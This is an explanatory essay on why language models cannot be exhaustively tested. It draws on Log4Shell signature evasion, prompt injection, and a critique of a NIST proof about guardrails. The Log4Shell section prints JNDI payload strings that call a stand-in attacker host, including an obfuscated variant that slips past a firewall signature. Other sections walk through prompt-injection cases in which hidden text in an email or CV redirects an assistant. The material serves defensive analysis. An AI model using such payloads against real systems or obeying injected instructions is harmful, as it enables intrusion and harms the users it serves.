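# Why language models cannot be tested on every possible input, and what testing can still do

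## Tokens, prompts and why they cannot all be tried

A large language model is a computer program that takes in text and produces text. Companies build chatbots, coding assistants and customer-service systems on such models. Increasingly, they also run them as agents, which can send emails, run code or browse the web. Developers test these systems by sending them inputs, called prompts, and checking whether the responses are acceptable. The most thorough method would be exhaustive testing, which means running a system on every input it can receive and checking each result. For a language model, this is feasible only on very small sets of inputs, mostly because there are too many possible prompts.

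### How text becomes tokens

Before a language model processes text, a separate program called a tokenizer cuts it into tokens, which are often words or parts of words, and replaces each token with a number. The model works on these numbers rather than directly on letters or words. OpenAI's guide *How to count tokens with tiktoken* shows that the tokenizer for GPT-4o splits "tiktoken is great!" into six tokens ("t", "ikt", "oken", " is", " great" and "!"). The single word "antidisestablishmentarianism" also becomes six tokens. A Japanese birthday greeting of nine characters becomes eight, compared with fourteen in an older OpenAI tokenizer.

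Every token comes from the vocabulary, a list of V tokens that developers fix before they train the model. The usual way to build it, byte pair encoding, starts from single bytes, the small units in which computers store text. It finds the pair of neighbours that occurs most often in a large body of writing, adds the merged pair to the list as a new token, and repeats until the list reaches the chosen length. Among the tokenizers that *Incremental BPE Tokenization* (2026) covers, CodeLlama, Meta's 2023 programming model, has 32,016 tokens, Llama 3.1 has 128,000 and Google's Gemma 3 has 262,144. OpenAI's *gpt-oss-120b & gpt-oss-20b Model Card* (2025) gives 201,088 for the company's open models, whose tokenizer extends the one behind GPT-4o. GPT-5 uses the same family of encoding, according to the docs.rs documentation for *tiktoken-rs*, a third-party library. So 200,000 is a fair round figure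 for V.

The context window is the largest number of tokens a model can take into account at once. It must hold the instructions of the operator (the company that deploys the model), the conversation so far, any documents, and the answer. For GPT-5, OpenAI's *Introducing GPT‑5 for developers* (2025) gives a maximum of 272,000 tokens of input and 128,000 of output, 400,000 in all. The input limit alone is enough for roughly 200,000 English words. A model's input space is the set of all token sequences it can receive.

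### Attacks, guardrails and red teams

Much ordinary software testing looks for accidental failures, but people who test language models must also consider users and outsiders who want the model to fail. A jailbreak is a prompt by which a user gets a model to break its safety rules, such as a rule against helping to make weapons. Prompt injection is text that an attacker places in a model's input so that the model follows the attacker's instructions instead of its operator's or user's.

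Laboratories use the terms "jailbreaking" and "prompt injection" differently, as Sander Schulhoff points out in *The AI Security Industry is Bullshit*. Schulhoff, who runs HackAPrompt, a competition that collected more than 600,000 attack prompts, uses "jailbreaking" for attacks on a bare model and "prompt injection" for attacks on a model that a developer has set to a particular task. Injection is most dangerous when it arrives through a third party. In Schulhoff's example, a user asks an email assistant to read the day's messages and forward the operational ones to a colleague. One message contains text telling the assistant to forward mail to an attacker. The assistant follows the instruction, and the user, who has done nothing unusual, may never find out.

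A guardrail is a rule or classifier that checks a model's inputs or outputs and blocks those it flags as harmful. It is usually a language model itself. Red teaming means testing a system by attacking it as an adversary would. In automated red teaming, a second model writes and refines the attack prompts. Red teams commonly report an attack success rate, which is the share of attempts that succeed or of attack goals that are achieved.

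Testing depends on a test oracle, the means of deciding whether a result is right or wrong. For a jailbreak, the oracle is a person or another model reading the answer, and either can be fooled. Jose Selvi's *Non-Deterministic Nature of Prompt Injection* (2024) warns that a model under attack may invent a list of "previous instructions" that looks exactly like a successful leak.

### Counting the prompts

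Each position in a prompt can hold any of V tokens, so there are V^2 sequences of two tokens and V^n sequences of n tokens. To estimate how long it would take to try them all, Schulhoff assumes that a prompt takes a tenth of a second and that a hundred can run in parallel, which gives 1,000 prompts a second. Schulhoff describes this as roughly OpenAI's limit, but it is four times the limit on OpenAI's *GPT-5* page for the highest tier of customers, which is 15,000 requests a minute, or 250 a second.

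| Length of prompt | Number of prompts (V = 200,000) | Time at 1,000 a second | Time at 250 a second |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 token | 200,000 | 200 seconds | 13 minutes |
| 2 tokens | 40 billion | 1.3 years | 5 years |
| 3 tokens | 8 × 10^15 | 250,000 years | 1 million years |
| 4 tokens | 1.6 × 10^21 | 51 billion years | 200 billion years |

At Schulhoff's rate, trying the four-token prompts alone would take between three and four times the age of the universe, which is about 13.8 billion years. A four-token prompt is a phrase like "How are you today". Faster machines help very little, because each further token multiplies the work by 200,000. A computer 200,000 times as fast could try prompts only one token longer in the same time. A smaller vocabulary also helps very little. With CodeLlama's 32,016 tokens, at the same rate, the four-token prompts would take 33 million years and the five-token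 prompts about a trillion years.

Cost limits exhaustive testing even sooner than time does. GPT-5's list price is $10 per million output tokens. Even if the model answered every prompt with a single token, which is shorter than any real answer, the output for all the two-token prompts would cost $400,000, and for all the three-token prompts $80 billion.

Schulhoff's best-known figure is the number of possible prompts that fit in the whole window of a model like GPT-5, which the post gives as a one followed by a million zeros. The post does not show the calculation. With a vocabulary of 200,000 tokens, each token in the prompt adds about 5.301 digits to the count (the base-10 logarithm of 200,000), so an input of 272,000 tokens gives about 1.44 million digits. A million zeros would match an input of only about 189,000 tokens. Schulhoff's figure is therefore too low, by a factor that itself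 has more than 440,000 digits, but this does not affect the argument. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra* page lists a window of 1,050,000 tokens for that newer model and a maximum input of 922,000, which gives about 4.89 million digits. Both models also accept images, which these calculations leave out.

The formula counts only prompts of the full length, but including all the shorter ones would raise the total by just one part in 200,000. It also counts token sequences that no typed text ever produces. For example, the model could in principle receive "tiktoken" as eight single-letter tokens, but the tokenizer always splits the word into the same, smaller set of tokens. Counting texts instead of token sequences gives a safe lower limit. A string of 272,000 lower-case letters and spaces takes at most one token per character, so it always fits in the window, and there are 27^272,000 such strings, a number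 with about 389,000 digits. The true count for typed text therefore has between about 389,000 and 1.44 million digits.

Schulhoff argues that when vendors advertise guardrails that catch 99% of attacks, nobody could fully check the claim within the age of the universe, because there are too many possible prompts. This is true, but a random sample can estimate the rate, just as pollsters do not need to question every voter. The sample's precision depends on its size and hardly at all on the number of possible prompts. Schulhoff's stronger objection, in the same post, is that vendors usually test on a fixed collection of prompts that people wrote to attack other models, while attackers who adjust their prompts to the guardrail get through far more often. Such a sample would be misleading even if there were few possible prompts.

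### Leaving out the gibberish

Nearly all of these sequences are random tokens that no person would write, so one might propose testing only the prompts that mean something.

The classic way to estimate the number of plausible English texts comes from Claude Shannon's 1951 paper *Prediction and Entropy of Printed English*, in which he asked people to guess a text letter by letter. In one trial, a subject guessed 89 of 129 letters correctly at the first attempt. In another, a subject who could see the 100 preceding letters guessed the next one at the first attempt in 80 cases out of 100. Because English is so predictable, each letter carries little information. Shannon measured that information as entropy, the average number of bits per letter that the most efficient possible code would need. He concluded that the entropy of ordinary literary English is "of the order of one bit per letter",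 compared with 4.7 bits for a letter drawn at random from a 26-letter alphabet.

At an entropy of one bit per character, an efficient code turns a typical text of 1,000 characters, a longish paragraph, into about 1,000 binary digits. There are 2^1,000 strings of that length, so there are about 10^301 such paragraphs. *Tokka-Bench* (2026) reports an average of 4.25 bytes per token for gpt-oss, so 1,000 characters come to about 235 tokens. There are about 10^1,246 arbitrary sequences of 235 tokens. Excluding the gibberish reduces that to about 10^301, which is still far more than the number of atoms in the universe, which Schulhoff puts at 10^80.

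One bit per character is a rough figure. Teahan and Cleary (1996), in *The Entropy of English Using PPM-Based Models*, give Shannon's bounds as 0.6 and 1.3 bits per character, which puts the number of paragraphs between 10^181 and 10^391. Shannon thought that the entropy levelled off after about 100 characters of context. Scheibner and colleagues (2025), in *Large language models and the entropy of English*, used language models as the guessers and found that in many texts it keeps falling out to around 10,000 characters, so the value for long texts may be lower still. Even so, the entropy would have to fall to about a quarter of a bit per character before the number of plausible paragraphs came down to the number of atoms.

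Researchers also treat this restricted space as too large to list. *Model-diff* (Liu, Li and colleagues, 2024) aims to compare two language models on all the inputs that a model rates as likely text, which is a workable definition of text that people can understand. The paper describes the space of token sequences as finite but computationally impossible to enumerate, and it samples from the likely part.

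Restricting tests to sensible prompts also misses some attacks, because attackers don't have to write plausible English. Narek Maloyan (2026), in *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models*, describes the search for harmful prompts as optimisation over a discrete space of texts. Some methods in that literature use a computer search to find strings to append to an ordinary request, and many of these strings look like gibberish.

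### One prompt, many answers

The count so far includes only one check per prompt. That would be enough for a calculator, which returns the same answer every time, but a language model can answer the same prompt in different ways. It produces its answer one token at a time. At each step it computes a score for every token in the vocabulary, and a sampling procedure then picks one, usually with some randomness. A setting called temperature controls how random the choice is.

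Selvi, who works at the security firm NCC Group, showed how this affects a test. The operator's instructions told a model how to respond, and the user's input tried to override them. The first attempt failed, and a tester who stopped there would have recorded the application as safe. Selvi then sent the identical input several more times, and the attack succeeded. This is a reason to repeat each attack, or small variations of it, many times.

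If a prompt produces a harmful answer one time in a hundred, a single trial misses the problem 99% of the time, and it takes about 300 trials to have a 95% chance of seeing it at least once. Running every two-token prompt 300 times would lengthen the test from 1.3 years to about 380. Testers cannot always switch the randomness off. LiteLLM, a company that routes requests to many models, notes in its *GPT-6 Astra* announcement that this model accepts no temperature setting while its reasoning is on.

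In a conversation, the model's replies also become part of its input. Each reply joins the context window and affects the next response, so two testers who open with the same message can soon be testing different inputs. The effect is larger for agents, which make tool calls, or requests to run a program, search the web or open a file. The result of each call enters the window, and OpenAI advertised GPT-5 as able to chain together dozens of calls. OpenAI's guide to *GPT-6 Astra* describes workflows of many steps across code, browsers and professional software. Maloyan writes that input sequences in such systems are "formed dynamically from different sources". A tester chooses the opening request but has little control over what follows. Some inputs, such as an email that somebody will send next week, do not exist at the time of the test.

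### Finite or unbounded

A language model's input space is finite if its context window is fixed. With a vocabulary of V tokens and a window of n tokens, the model can receive V + V^2 + … + V^n different sequences. Someone with unlimited time and paper could write a table of every possible prompt with an acceptable answer beside each, and check the model against it.

There are infinitely many finite token sequences, because another token can always be added to any of them, so no finite table could list them all. This unbounded set is a better description of language in general, and of an agent that runs indefinitely, than a set capped by the context window. When an agent's history outgrows the window, the software around the model can drop or summarise older material and carry on, so the window doesn't limit the length of the run. The agent may also keep notes in files and reread them later,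 so an action at step 10,000 can depend on a web page from step 3.

Whether the set of possible prompts is infinite or only very large makes no practical difference to testers, who would run out of time before trying every four-token prompt in either case. It does matter for proofs, because an argument that assumes there is always a longer prompt holds for the set of all finite sequences but needs a further step to apply to a model with a fixed context window.

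### The objection from ordinary software

Most ordinary programs also have too many possible inputs to test them all, yet people trust software to run banks and aircraft, so a huge input space alone does not make a system untrustworthy.

In *Notes on Structured Programming* (1970), the Dutch computer scientist Edsger Dijkstra considered how to test a circuit in his university's computer that multiplied two 27-bit whole numbers. There are 2^54 such multiplications, about 1.8 × 10^16, and at some tens of microseconds each, testing them all would have taken more than 10,000 years. The circuit would perform only a negligible fraction of them during its working life, but users needed every one to be right because nobody could know in advance which ones would come up. Testing a sample could miss whole classes of critical cases. Dijkstra concluded that testing "can be used to show the presence of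 bugs", but never their absence.

A processor that did a billion multiplications a second could now finish the 2^54 cases in this example in about seven months. But the argument still holds for the 64-bit multipliers in present-day computers, which people rely on all the time. They have 2^128 possible inputs, more than the number of seven-token prompts for a model with V = 200,000.

That is reasonable because engineers do not treat the multiplier as a black box, which can be judged only by its outputs. Dijkstra's remedy was to take the structure of the mechanism into account. Arithmetic specifies the right answer to every case, so the tester has a perfect oracle, a way to tell whether any output is correct. The inputs also fall into classes that the mechanism treats alike, so one argument can cover a whole class.

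The same notes give the example of a two-line program with two numbers, r and dd, where r starts out at least zero and smaller than dd. The program halves dd and then, if dd is no larger than r, subtracts dd from r. Dijkstra proves that r is still at least zero and smaller than dd at the end. After the halving, r is smaller than twice dd. If dd is larger than r, the program does nothing more and the condition already holds. Otherwise, r is at least dd and smaller than twice dd, so subtracting dd leaves it at least zero and smaller than dd. These two cases cover every pair of numbers to which the program applies, without running it. For programs with loops, Dijkstra extends the method with mathematical induction. If a statement holds at the start and each round of the loop preserves it, then it holds after any number of rounds.

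An argument like this needs a specification, which language models mostly lack. Some narrow tasks have one, such as adding numbers or producing a file in a set format. But there is no specification of "be helpful and avoid harm" that a computer could check, and whether an answer is acceptable often depends on who is asking and why. Schulhoff observes that it is easier to instruct a model never to do something than to do it only sometimes. An email assistant has to send messages in some situations and refuse in others, and nobody has written a full list of those situations.

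Proof is difficult for a different reason. A model's developers can inspect every number inside it, but those numbers do not form a series of steps with a statement that provably holds before and after each one, as Dijkstra's two lines do. A certificate is a proof that a system behaves as required on every input in a stated set, and for language models these sets are narrow. Dijkstra also noted that if each of N components is correct with probability p, the whole program is correct with probability roughly p^N. The same applies to agents. If each of fifty steps independently goes right 99% of the time, all fifty go right only about 60% of the time.

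The classes of equivalent inputs are the hardest thing to replace. An engineer knows from the multiplier's circuit why a result for one pair of numbers carries over to others. A language model can respond differently to two prompts that mean the same thing to a person because, according to Maloyan, its learned mapping is sensitive to small variations in tokens. Translating a prompt is a well-known way to get around a guardrail, and people in the security industry told Schulhoff that many commercial products depend heavily on how they perform in English.

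## Log4Shell: one attack string written in endless ways

Log4Shell is a security flaw in Log4j, a free logging library for Java programs, that became public in December 2021. Attackers could write the text that triggered it in an unlimited number of ways, so filters that searched for known spellings kept missing new ones, much as a guardrail can miss a translated request. Engineers still repaired the flaw by the end of that month without having to list the spellings. They knew exactly how Log4j turned each one into an action, so they could treat them all as one class, as Dijkstra recommended for the multiplier.

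### How a log entry could run code

Most server software keeps a log, a running record of what it does and who contacts it. Thousands of software packages do this with Log4j, a library that volunteers maintain under the Apache Software Foundation. A web server might log the address each visitor requests, the name of the visitor's browser and the user name in each login attempt, all of which is text that strangers choose.

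Log4j supported lookups, short expressions that the library replaced with a value, such as the date or the version of Java on the machine. Lookups are useful in the settings that a program's developers write, but Log4j also evaluated any lookup it found inside a message, even if the message came from a stranger.

In July 2013, the project accepted a new kind of lookup from a member of its community. It used the Java Naming and Directory Interface (JNDI), through which Java programs fetch items from directory servers. According to Everson, Cheng and Zhang, in *Log4shell*, a 2022 workshop paper, the requester wanted better logs without having to program each item separately. The result was that a simple logging system became a command interpreter. An attack had four steps:

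1. The attacker sends the target some text, for example in place of a browser name, that contains a JNDI lookup with the address of the attacker's own server.
2. The target program hands the text to Log4j to record.
3. Log4j recognises the lookup and sends a request to that address, typically using LDAP, a protocol for directory servers.
4. The attacker's server replies with Java code, or with the location of some, and the target runs it.

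The attacker needed no password, and no user had to click on anything. As Everson and colleagues point out, a web server that was not itself vulnerable could receive the text and pass it on to a database, a billing program or a security monitor, and the attack would start when one of those logged it with a vulnerable copy of Log4j.

### From private report to public attack

The Cyber Safety Review Board, a US government panel that examined major security incidents, set out the dates of the disclosure and repair in its *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022). An engineer at Alibaba Cloud reported the flaw privately to Apache on 24 November 2021. The maintainers worked on the repair in a public code repository and tagged a release candidate, a near-final version of the repaired library, on 6 December. Some accounts give that day as the date of the fix, but Apache released version 2.15.0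 to the general public on 10 December.

It had planned to release the new version later. On 9 December, a Chinese security company used the messaging service WeChat to post a partly obscured screenshot of a working attack. The Board thought it likely that somebody had worked out the flaw from the release candidate, but could not confirm this. In *Exploitation of Log4j CVE-2021-44228 before public disclosure*, Graham-Cumming and Martinho give the time of the disclosure on Twitter as 14:25 UTC that day. Their employer, Cloudflare, filters traffic for many websites and recorded the first attempted attack nine minutes later.

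Cloudflare had also recorded three attempts on 1 December. A technology company told the Board about activity from that date and judged it consistent with tests of the Alibaba engineer's own demonstration. The Board found no other sign that the flaw was used before its disclosure. The flaw, officially identified as CVE-2021-44228, received the highest possible severity score, 10.0.

### Why signatures failed

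Updating every affected machine takes time, so many organisations relied at first on a web application firewall (WAF), a filter in front of a website that blocks requests matching known attack patterns. A signature is a fixed text pattern by which such a filter recognises an attack. Gero (2022), in *A Log4j Retrospective Part 3*, explains the weakness with a deliberately simple signature. Gero works at Akamai, which delivers and protects web traffic. The signature consists of seven characters in a row:

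`${jndi:`

It catches the plain form of the attack, in which the attacker asks a website for this address:

`/${jndi:ldap://rce.malware.example/a}`

But the attacker can also write:

`/${${lower:J}ndi:ldap://rce.malware.example/a}`

The seven characters no longer appear in a row, so the firewall lets the request through. Log4j then evaluates the inner expression, which means "J in lower case", and replaces it with j. This produces the plain address, and Log4j carries out the lookup. The dangerous string did not yet exist when the firewall inspected the text.

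The words "jndi" and "ldap" have eight letters in total. Suppose an attacker can write each letter in four ways, either plainly or through one of three lookups that return it. The string then has 4^8 = 65,536 versions, which a computer could easily store and search for. However, the text inside a lookup can itself be a lookup. With up to two layers and three choices at each layer, each letter has 1 + 3 + 9 = 13 spellings, and the string has 13^8, or about 816 million. With up to three layers, each letter has 40 spellings and the string has 6.6 trillion. The notation allows any number of layers, so the number of versions is limited only by how long a text the server accepts and how deeply nested an expression it can process.

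Attackers used a tiny part of this variety, but it was enough to defeat simple rules. Graham-Cumming and Martinho report that the earliest attacks used plain strings, which simple rules blocked, and that attackers then began to disguise them. Some used general tricks, such as replacing characters with numeric codes, which any capable firewall can reverse before it checks its signatures. Others used Log4j's own lookups, which a firewall can undo only if its rules account for Log4j's notation. Cloudflare blocked an average of 5,483 requests a minute on 10 December and 27,439 on 12 December. Plain strings stayed popular even after disguises spread, presumably because many targets had no filter.

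Akamai's *Threat Intelligence on Log4j CVE* describes the same shift in more detail. Within hours, attackers replaced LDAP with other protocols, since some filters searched for that word. They then hid letters behind lookups that change upper case to lower case, and later behind lookups that return a default value. In the following days they added expressions that evaluate to nothing and could be placed between any two letters. Some variants did not work. About 57% of the machines sending attacks were already known to Akamai from earlier campaigns, so established attackers did much of this experimenting.

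Palo Alto Networks, another security company, counted 51,500 attempts that used only 442 different strings in the browser-name field. The number of distinct disguises may be smaller, because strings that use the same disguise but different server addresses count as different.

### One normal form

However an attacker spelled the string, Log4j replaced the inner lookups with their values until it had a plain JNDI request. This request is the normal form, the single version to which many equivalent inputs reduce. Fastly's *Log4Shell attacks (CVE-2021-44228) insights* lists several spellings from the company's logs that all evaluate to the same string. A filter that makes the same replacements as Log4j, but does not send the request, can therefore recognise all these spellings with one signature.

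The Daily Swig's *Open source utility exposes payloads without running vulnerable Java code* reports on Ox4Shell, a tool that undoes the disguise on an attacker's string and shows an analyst what the string would do. Daniel Abeles and Ron Vider of the security firm Oxeye presented it at the Black Hat USA conference.

Some lookups return values available only on the target machine, such as its environment settings, so a filter elsewhere on the network may not be able to evaluate the string exactly. An attacker can also write a lookup that refers to itself, so the replacement never finishes and the string has no normal form. Log4j crashed on such input until version 2.17.0. A filter needs to stop after a certain number of steps and treat the text as hostile.

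Core Rule Set's *CRS and Log4j / Log4Shell / CVE-2021-44228* (2021) describes a way to detect the attack string without evaluating its lookups. Core Rule Set is a free collection of firewall rules. Its developers reasoned that every lookup starts with a dollar sign and an opening brace, `${`. Either the word "jndi" appears openly in the lookup, or at least one of its letters comes from another lookup nested inside it. Searching for the word itself and for one `${` inside another therefore covers every spelling, however many layers it has. The developers also found from Log4j's source code that an attacker could not break up the pattern with spaces, because spaces would ruin the lookup.

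Dijkstra used this kind of argument for the two-line program, where he covered every pair of numbers by dividing them into cases. An unlimited number of attack strings does not by itself defeat a finite filter.

The rule can block legitimate requests that contain nested lookups, but the developers accepted this because the flaw was so serious. Everson and colleagues are more doubtful about firewalls, warning that covering every possible value might block too much normal traffic. They also point out that some programs receive data in Base64, a code that represents any data in 64 ordinary characters, and decode it before logging it. The nesting rule misses attacks sent this way because the firewall checks only the encoded text, in which no lookup is visible. Graham-Cumming and Martinho add that logged data does not always arrive through the internet, so even a perfect firewall would have left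 some paths open.

### Four releases in one month

Apache fixed the problem over four releases by changing what Log4j did with the text. The version numbers here are for Java 8 and later. Apache issued parallel fixes for older versions of Java.

| Version | Date in December 2021 | What it changed | What remained possible |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2.15.0 | 10 | Turned off lookups in messages by default and limited JNDI connections to the local machine by default | Attacks through other logged data in some configurations |
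| 2.16.0 | 13 | Removed lookups in messages and turned off JNDI by default | Crashing a program with a lookup that refers to itself, in some configurations |
| 2.17.0 | 17 | Stopped evaluating lookups inside logged data and limited JNDI to Java's own protocol | Running code, for someone who could already edit the logging configuration |
| 2.17.1 | 27 | Put the same protocol limit on the database connections that Log4j uses for storing logs | |

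Version 2.15.0 was incomplete because a stranger's text could also enter outside the log message. Programs can attach extra values to each log entry, such as the visitor's browser name, and some configurations used a lookup to insert these values. Log4j then evaluated the inserted text as well. Apache first rated this second flaw as moderate, with a score of 3.7, because it believed the flaw could only disrupt the service. It raised the score to 9.0 after researchers used the flaw to run code on several operating systems. Apache also withdrew its earlier advice to switch off message lookups through a setting, because other parts of the library could still evaluate them. The maintainers missed some of these paths at first, even though they could read all of the code.

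Version 2.17.0 dealt with the whole class of attack strings. According to Apache, Log4j still evaluates lookups within lookups when it reads its own configuration, which contains no text from strangers. When it handles a log entry, it inserts any text from a stranger without evaluating it again. For example, a configuration can tell Log4j to write each message in lower case. The message "Hello, World!" then becomes "hello, world!", but if the message is a lookup expression, Log4j writes it into the log as ordinary text, however the expression is spelled.

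Apache could remove message lookups without much disruption because almost nobody needed them. When Apache proposed turning the feature off, it noted that a search of GitHub and Stack Overflow, where programmers share code and questions, had found no sign that anyone used it. The feature also wasted computing time by making every program search every message for lookups.

Apache's *Security*, the project's current account of what it defends against, assumes attackers will send text that looks like lookup syntax, including text designed to trigger endless evaluation. It tells developers that log messages need no particular validation. It lists 2.17.0 as the fix for the fourth flaw, but the original advisory and the Cyber Safety Review Board both list 2.17.1.

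The repair protects only the systems where someone installs it. The Board called Log4j an "endemic vulnerability" and expected unrepaired copies to remain in use for perhaps a decade or longer. Finding the copies was a large part of the work because there was no list of the products that contained the library. One US federal department reported spending 33,000 hours on its response.

### How testers confirmed a hit

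A tester who sends the attack string to a website usually learns nothing from the reply, because the lookup happens inside the logging software. Testers therefore put the address of a server they controlled in the lookup. If that server received a request from the target, Log4j had evaluated the string. Attackers used the same method to search for victims, and Akamai found that most of these attackers relied on popular online services that report such requests.

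Everson and colleagues distinguish three levels of this test. The simplest uses a special web address and notifies the tester when any machine looks it up, which suggests that the target is vulnerable. In the next, the tester's own server records a connection from the target and can often get it to reveal its name or Java version. The most demanding test carries out the whole attack, running harmless code on the target, which gives much more certainty.

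A target that sends no callback may still be vulnerable. The firewall may have blocked this spelling but not others, the tester may have put the string in a field that the program does not log, or the program may not process its data until hours later. The US cybersecurity agency CISA published a scanner that tries the plain attack and 23 disguised variants in more than 60 request headers and seven common form fields, but an attacker could still use a variant that the scanner doesn't try. Everson and colleagues conclude that a penetration test, in which testers attack a system to find its weaknesses, can prove that a system is exploitable but never that it is safe, which is the same objection Dijkstra had to testing in general.

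Organisations could check for Log4Shell by searching the files on their own machines for vulnerable versions of the library. This was a better method than sending attack strings. A machine with a repaired copy is safe from every spelling of the attack, so checking the version number removes the need to test each spelling.

A defence could also ignore the text. Everson and colleagues put a firewall between a vulnerable program and an attacker's server, then tried two attacks, one that ran code on the target and one that stole information from it. Both succeeded without a defence and failed when the firewall stopped the target from opening new outside connections. Removing the JNDI component also stopped them, as did the setting that Apache later withdrew. The test program used Log4j only in its simplest form, so the experiment could not test the other paths that made that setting inadequate.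 Blocking connections does not depend on which path the text takes, because both types of attack need the target to contact the attacker's server.

### Where prompts differ

The comparison with prompts holds for filters that match the wording of a text. A rule that blocks a phrase from earlier attacks fails when an attacker rewords it, just as Gero's signature fails on a nested lookup. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), warns developers against such lists of forbidden content because there are infinite ways to rephrase an attack. The NCSC published his article, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, in December 2025.

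Better filters could catch every spelling of the Log4Shell string because Log4j's lookups follow a known grammar. The source code defines what counts as a lookup, even down to the effect of a space, and every disguised JNDI lookup had to contain a second opening mark. The prompts that lead a language model to break its rules have no such grammar, so developers cannot name a feature that every disguise must contain. Models can also follow disguises that someone invents within the prompt itself. *Experimental Evaluation of Non-Natural Language Prompt Injection Attacks on LLMs* reports that defences designed for natural language become ineffective against unusual or unstructured input.

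Prompts also lack a normal form. Log4j interprets the same string in the same way each time, given the same machine and settings, apart from values such as the date. An engineer can therefore copy its rules into a filter and know what the string will do. A model has no such rules to copy, and it may answer the same prompt differently each time, as in Selvi's test. A filter can undo standard encodings in a prompt, translate it into English or ask another model to summarise it. These steps help against known disguises, but the simplified prompt may not affect the protected model in the same way as the original. NIST, the US standards agency, has published a proof that no finite set of guardrails stops every prompt.

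The consequences of an attack on a language model are also harder to pin down. Running code through Log4Shell always required a JNDI lookup to a server the attacker chose, and engineers could block that lookup. A chatbot's harmful act may be only the words of its answer. An agent's could be any action its tools allow, such as sending a file, deleting a record or making a payment. David C advises developers to assume the worst an attacker could do with direct access to those tools.

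Apache removed message lookups with almost no effect on users, but a developer cannot remove a model's ability to follow instructions in text, because people use the model for that ability. An assistant that only summarises emails does not need permission to send them, but one that acts on requests in emails has to let other people's text influence its actions.

The result of a Log4Shell test was also clear, because the callback either arrived or did not, whereas a jailbreak test relies on a fallible judge. A prompt injection test against an agent can be just as clear as the Log4Shell test if the tester plants an instruction to send a message to a test account and checks whether the message arrives. The result is less clear when the harm is subtle, for example if an injected sentence leads the assistant to recommend the wrong supplier. In all of these cases, one failed attack is little evidence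 that the next wording will fail too.

### The lesson of SQL injection

David C's article does not discuss Log4Shell, but its argument about SQL injection, a related and much older attack, explains why the Log4Shell repair has no equivalent for language models. SQL is a language for giving commands to databases. A careless website builds a command by joining its own text to whatever a visitor has typed, so a visitor who types a piece of SQL can make the database carry it out. The standard repair is the parameterised query, in which the program sends the command separately from the visitor's data, and the database never interprets that data as an instruction. Version 2.17.0 of Log4j follows much the same principle, as it evaluates its own configuration but not the text that strangers supply.

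Prompt injection looks like another case of a system mistaking data for instructions. In David C's example, a recruiter's system asks a model to score a CV in which the candidate has hidden a sentence telling the model to approve it. But a database handles commands and data separately, and a parameterised query enforces the separation, whereas a language model receives the recruiter's instructions and the CV as one sequence of tokens and predicts the next token from all of it. Developers can train a model to prioritise their instructions, mark the parts of a prompt that are data, or try to detect attacks. David C regards these as attempts to impose a distinction on a technology that does not have one, and concludes that there is "a good chance" that prompt injection will never have a full remedy like the one for SQL injection.

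The argument shows that current models, because of the way they process text, offer no guarantee against attacks. It does not show how often attacks succeed, and according to the article, marking data and similar techniques do make them harder. A future model might have a separate channel for instructions. That would help with the CV, which should never be treated as instructions. It would help less when a user tells an assistant to "do what my colleague asks in this email", because the user wants the assistant to follow instructions in the email, and the assistant has to judge which of the colleague's requests to carry out.

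David C proposes thinking of a model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that someone with fewer permissions tricks into misusing its own. Ordinary confused deputies can be repaired, but for a language model David C recommends reducing both the likelihood and the impact of an attack, above all through safeguards outside the model that restrict what the system can do. The CaMeL system does this by limiting an agent's actions whatever it reads, and the firewall that blocked outgoing connections from Log4j worked on the same principle.

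The article also describes a rule from a discussion between the programmers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes text from some party, its permissions should drop to those of that party. An assistant that reads email from strangers would then have no access to tools that a stranger should not control. The rule makes many convenient products impossible, including an assistant that reads all of a user's mail and can forward any of it without asking. David C suggests that a language model may be the wrong technology for a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

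## NIST's proof that no finite set of guardrails stops every prompt

Vassilev (2025), in *Robust AI Security and Alignment*, argues that a limit applies to every AI system, whatever its design, whereas David C's doubts about prompt injection concern how current models process text. Vassilev, a senior scientist at NIST, adapts the logician Kurt Gödel's 1931 theorem about what mathematics can prove. The preprint appeared in December 2025 and the final version in *IEEE Security & Privacy* in May 2026. In June, NIST announced that, according to the proof, there will always be a way to prompt an AI system to disregard its rules.

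The theorem is correct for a system that accepts prompts of any length. But it is about which statements a program can prove, and the conclusion about jailbreaks does not follow from it. Other researchers have proved limits that do concern harmful text, each under assumptions about the model, the filter or the rules.

### Policies and checkers

An organisation that runs an AI system decides which prompts are unacceptable. Vassilev calls this decision a policy, written Π. A system is aligned if it processes the acceptable prompts and blocks the unacceptable ones. It is robust if it stays aligned when capable attackers try to make it break the policy.

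Vassilev calls every kind of guardrail a "checker", from cleaning training data to filtering a model's answers. Mathematically, a checker is a program that takes a statement T and a proposed proof p, and returns 1 if and only if T is true and p is a proof of T that it can verify. An ordinary guardrail, however, gives a verdict without proving anything.

The article uses Gödel's theorem in a form that the mathematician Gregory Chaitin published in 1974. For any checker, there is a true statement for which the checker accepts no proof at all. Vassilev's version adds that this statement can be about a forbidden prompt. The proof has six steps:

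1. There are infinitely many forbidden prompts. If there were only finitely many, one of them would be the longest, but adding a harmless opening sentence to it would give a longer prompt that is still forbidden.
2. Choose a whole number n. For each forbidden prompt x, consider the statement "every algorithm that outputs x is longer than n bits". There are fewer than 2^(n+1) programs of n bits or less, and each outputs at most one prompt, so the statement is true for infinitely many forbidden prompts.
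3. Write a search program that goes through the forbidden prompts and all possible proofs in order of length. It gives each combination to the checker. As soon as the checker accepts a proof of the statement for some x, the program outputs x and stops.
4. This search program is shorter than n bits if n is large enough. Only the number n itself changes in the program, and writing it down takes about log2(n) bits. If the rest of the program takes a million bits and n is two million, the whole program has about 1,000,021 bits.
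5. Suppose the program stops and outputs x. Then an algorithm shorter than n bits has output x, so the statement about x is false. But the checker accepts proofs only of true statements, so the program can never stop.
6. The program tries every forbidden prompt with every proof. Since it never stops, the checker accepts no proof of the statement for any forbidden prompt, although the statement is true for infinitely many of them.

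The argument resembles an old puzzle about "the smallest number that nobody can describe in under twenty words". That phrase seems to describe the number in eleven words.

### Why jailbreaks do not follow

Vassilev concludes from this theorem that any policy will fail to stop some adversarial prompts. But the unprovable statement is about the length of computer programs, and a guardrail can block a prompt without computing the length of the shortest program that outputs it.

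Suppose an organisation forbids every prompt that contains the word "explosive". Infinitely many prompts contain it, so the proof applies, and for some of them the statement about program length is true but unprovable. Yet a few lines of code can block all these prompts and allow all others by searching for the word. The theorem therefore does not imply that perfect guardrails are impossible. People can still ask about bombs without using the word, but that is a flaw in the policy rather than the guardrail.

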